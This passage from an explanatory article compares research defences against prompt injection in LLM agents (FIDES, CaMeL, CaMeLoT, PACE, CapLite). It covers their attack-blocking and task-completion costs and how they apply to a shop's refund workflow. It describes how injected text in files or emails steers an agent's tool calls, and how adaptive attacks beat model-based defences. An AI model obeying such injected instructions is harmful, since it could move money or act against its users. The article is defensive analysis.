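where ℓ_tool is the label on the choice of tool and ℓ₁ to ℓₙ are the labels on its arguments. A looser policy for sending messages requires a trusted recipient but accepts untrusted text in the body. This matches the distinction between the control plane and the data plane.

### What the labels cost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on the 97 tasks of AgentDojo. In each attack, the injected text came from someone who knew the agent's tools. The completion rates below are for runs without an attack and combine the published rates for the four parts of the benchmark, weighted by the number of tasks:

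| System | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 152 | 82% |
| Ordinary agent with policy checks | 0 | 41% |
| FIDES without policy checks | 21 | 61% |
| FIDES with policy checks | 0 | 52% |

The policy checks stopped every attack that was counted. They also halved the ordinary agent's completion rate, because one untrusted email in the context was enough to block most later actions. FIDES recovered some of those tasks by hiding the untrusted text in variables, but it still completed far fewer than the unprotected agent. Some of this loss came from GPT-4o's difficulty with variables. In the travel tasks, switching to OpenAI's reasoning model o1 raised completion from 41% to 68%.

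Completion fell from 98.8% to 52.5% on the banking tasks, which are the closest to the shop's work. Many of these tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policies block by design.

The labels in this test were also unusually good. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, but a shop can't know in advance which fields attackers will use. It would have to mark more fields and would probably block more legitimate tasks.

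Tests of CaMeL show similar losses. In *CaMeLoT* (2026), Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues ran it with Claude Haiku 4.5 on the same 97 tasks, without any attacks, and it completed 49. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that CaMeL blocked every attack with its policies on but completed far fewer tasks. With the policies off, 138 of 141 attacks in one category succeeded against one model. The program that CaMeL writes in advance therefore gives little protection against wrong values unless somebody also writes the policies.

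That program can fail too. In one task, the user told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The model wrote a loop that matched each instruction in the file to a tool, so the file determined which tools the program called. A shop that tells its agent to do whatever the customer asks risks the same problem.

### Successors in 2026

Newer systems try to lower these costs. CaMeLoT examines the program before it runs, so it can reject an unsafe one without calling any tools. One of its rules is:

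AG(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

AG means "at every point of every possible run". Under the rule, whenever the program sends money, neither the recipient nor the amount may come from untrusted data. If a program breaks a rule, CaMeLoT can show the model where and ask for a new version. In the test by Nikolaou and colleagues, where this repair step was mostly switched off, CaMeLoT completed 51 tasks, two more than CaMeL. Both systems blocked 17 harmless tasks, including six of the 16 banking tasks.

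PACE comes closer to the shop's caps. It turns the authenticated request into a permission with limits on purpose, resource, arguments and budget, and text from a model can't extend that permission. Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) report in *PACE* that it completed at most three percentage points fewer tasks than an unprotected agent on eight benchmarks. However, the version they tested can restore calls that one of its checks has blocked. Their full security guarantee applies to a stricter version, which they didn't test.

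*CapLite* (2026) describes a defence for small models. In tests on 15 of them, no attack succeeded against CapLite, while 20 of 13,935 succeeded against CaMeL. The two defences completed about the same share of tasks, but CapLite used far fewer tokens, the pieces of text by which providers usually charge. It used 17,100 per task, compared with 93,700 for CaMeL and 28,000 for the unprotected agent, so protection doesn't have to cost more.

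For agents that operate a computer screen, *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) found that a design based on CaMeL added 1.88 times the unprotected agent's total token use. A design based on FIDES added 29.6 times that total, because it resends the whole history to the planning model at every step.

No low-code platform seems to offer information-flow control yet. The published systems are research software, and *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that even CaMeL's restricted Python keeps features that make strong guarantees difficult. n8n already has one part of the design, since a workflow without an agent is a fixed program that outside text can't extend. But n8n's expressions copy a value without recording its origin, so the refund node can't distinguish a number from the orders table from a number that a model wrote.

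### Fixed limits or better models

Researchers disagree about whether agents need fixed limits. Willison argues that they do, because a defence that stops 99% of attacks fails against someone who keeps looking for the other 1%. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) cites evidence for this. Almost no attacks were reported to succeed against defences that rely on the model or its prompt, but more than 90% did once attackers adapted to them. Against one defence outside the model, 2.6% of adapted attacks succeeded, compared with 4.2% before adaptation, though this result is preliminary and comes from only three runs.

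The opposing view is that people use agents for tasks nobody planned in advance, and that fixed limits rule out those tasks. Results on AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, support this. *DRIFT* (2025) reports that CaMeL completed none of the AgentDyn tasks in any setting. *DRIFT* presents a competing defence with more flexible rules, so the comparison is not independent, but it also reports that every defence it tested did poorly on the benchmark. According to *AgentDyn* (2026), agents often stop to ask the user for confirmation, which lowers their scores, although a real user could answer.

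Better models strengthen the case for flexibility, but they also lose less performance under the limits. In the tests described earlier, a single attack on Claude Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time, while the FIDES results come from GPT-4o, a much weaker model. A shop with a current model would have fewer attacks left for the labels to stop, and it could monitor the agent's calls for those that remain. However, FIDES completed more tasks with o1, and Peters-Gill and colleagues found that the performance lost to separate channels tended to fall as models improved.

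Much of the disagreement is about different kinds of agent. The measured losses come from general assistants whose users may ask for almost anything. Nobody seems to have measured how many legitimate requests fail when a shop's workflow, rather than the model, sets the customer number and reads the refund amount from the shop's own table. Probably few do, since customers rarely need a refund on someone else's order or for more than they paid. These limits also stop accidental errors in those fields, which resistance to prompt injection doesn't.

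Monitoring works better for actions that are easy to undo. An employee can delete a bad draft, but a wrong refund appears in the log only after the money has left. The shop can therefore let the model write drafts freely and keep the narrow tool for refunds. If customer 417 asks for the 80 euros on a different card, the agent can draft a reply and pass the request to an employee.
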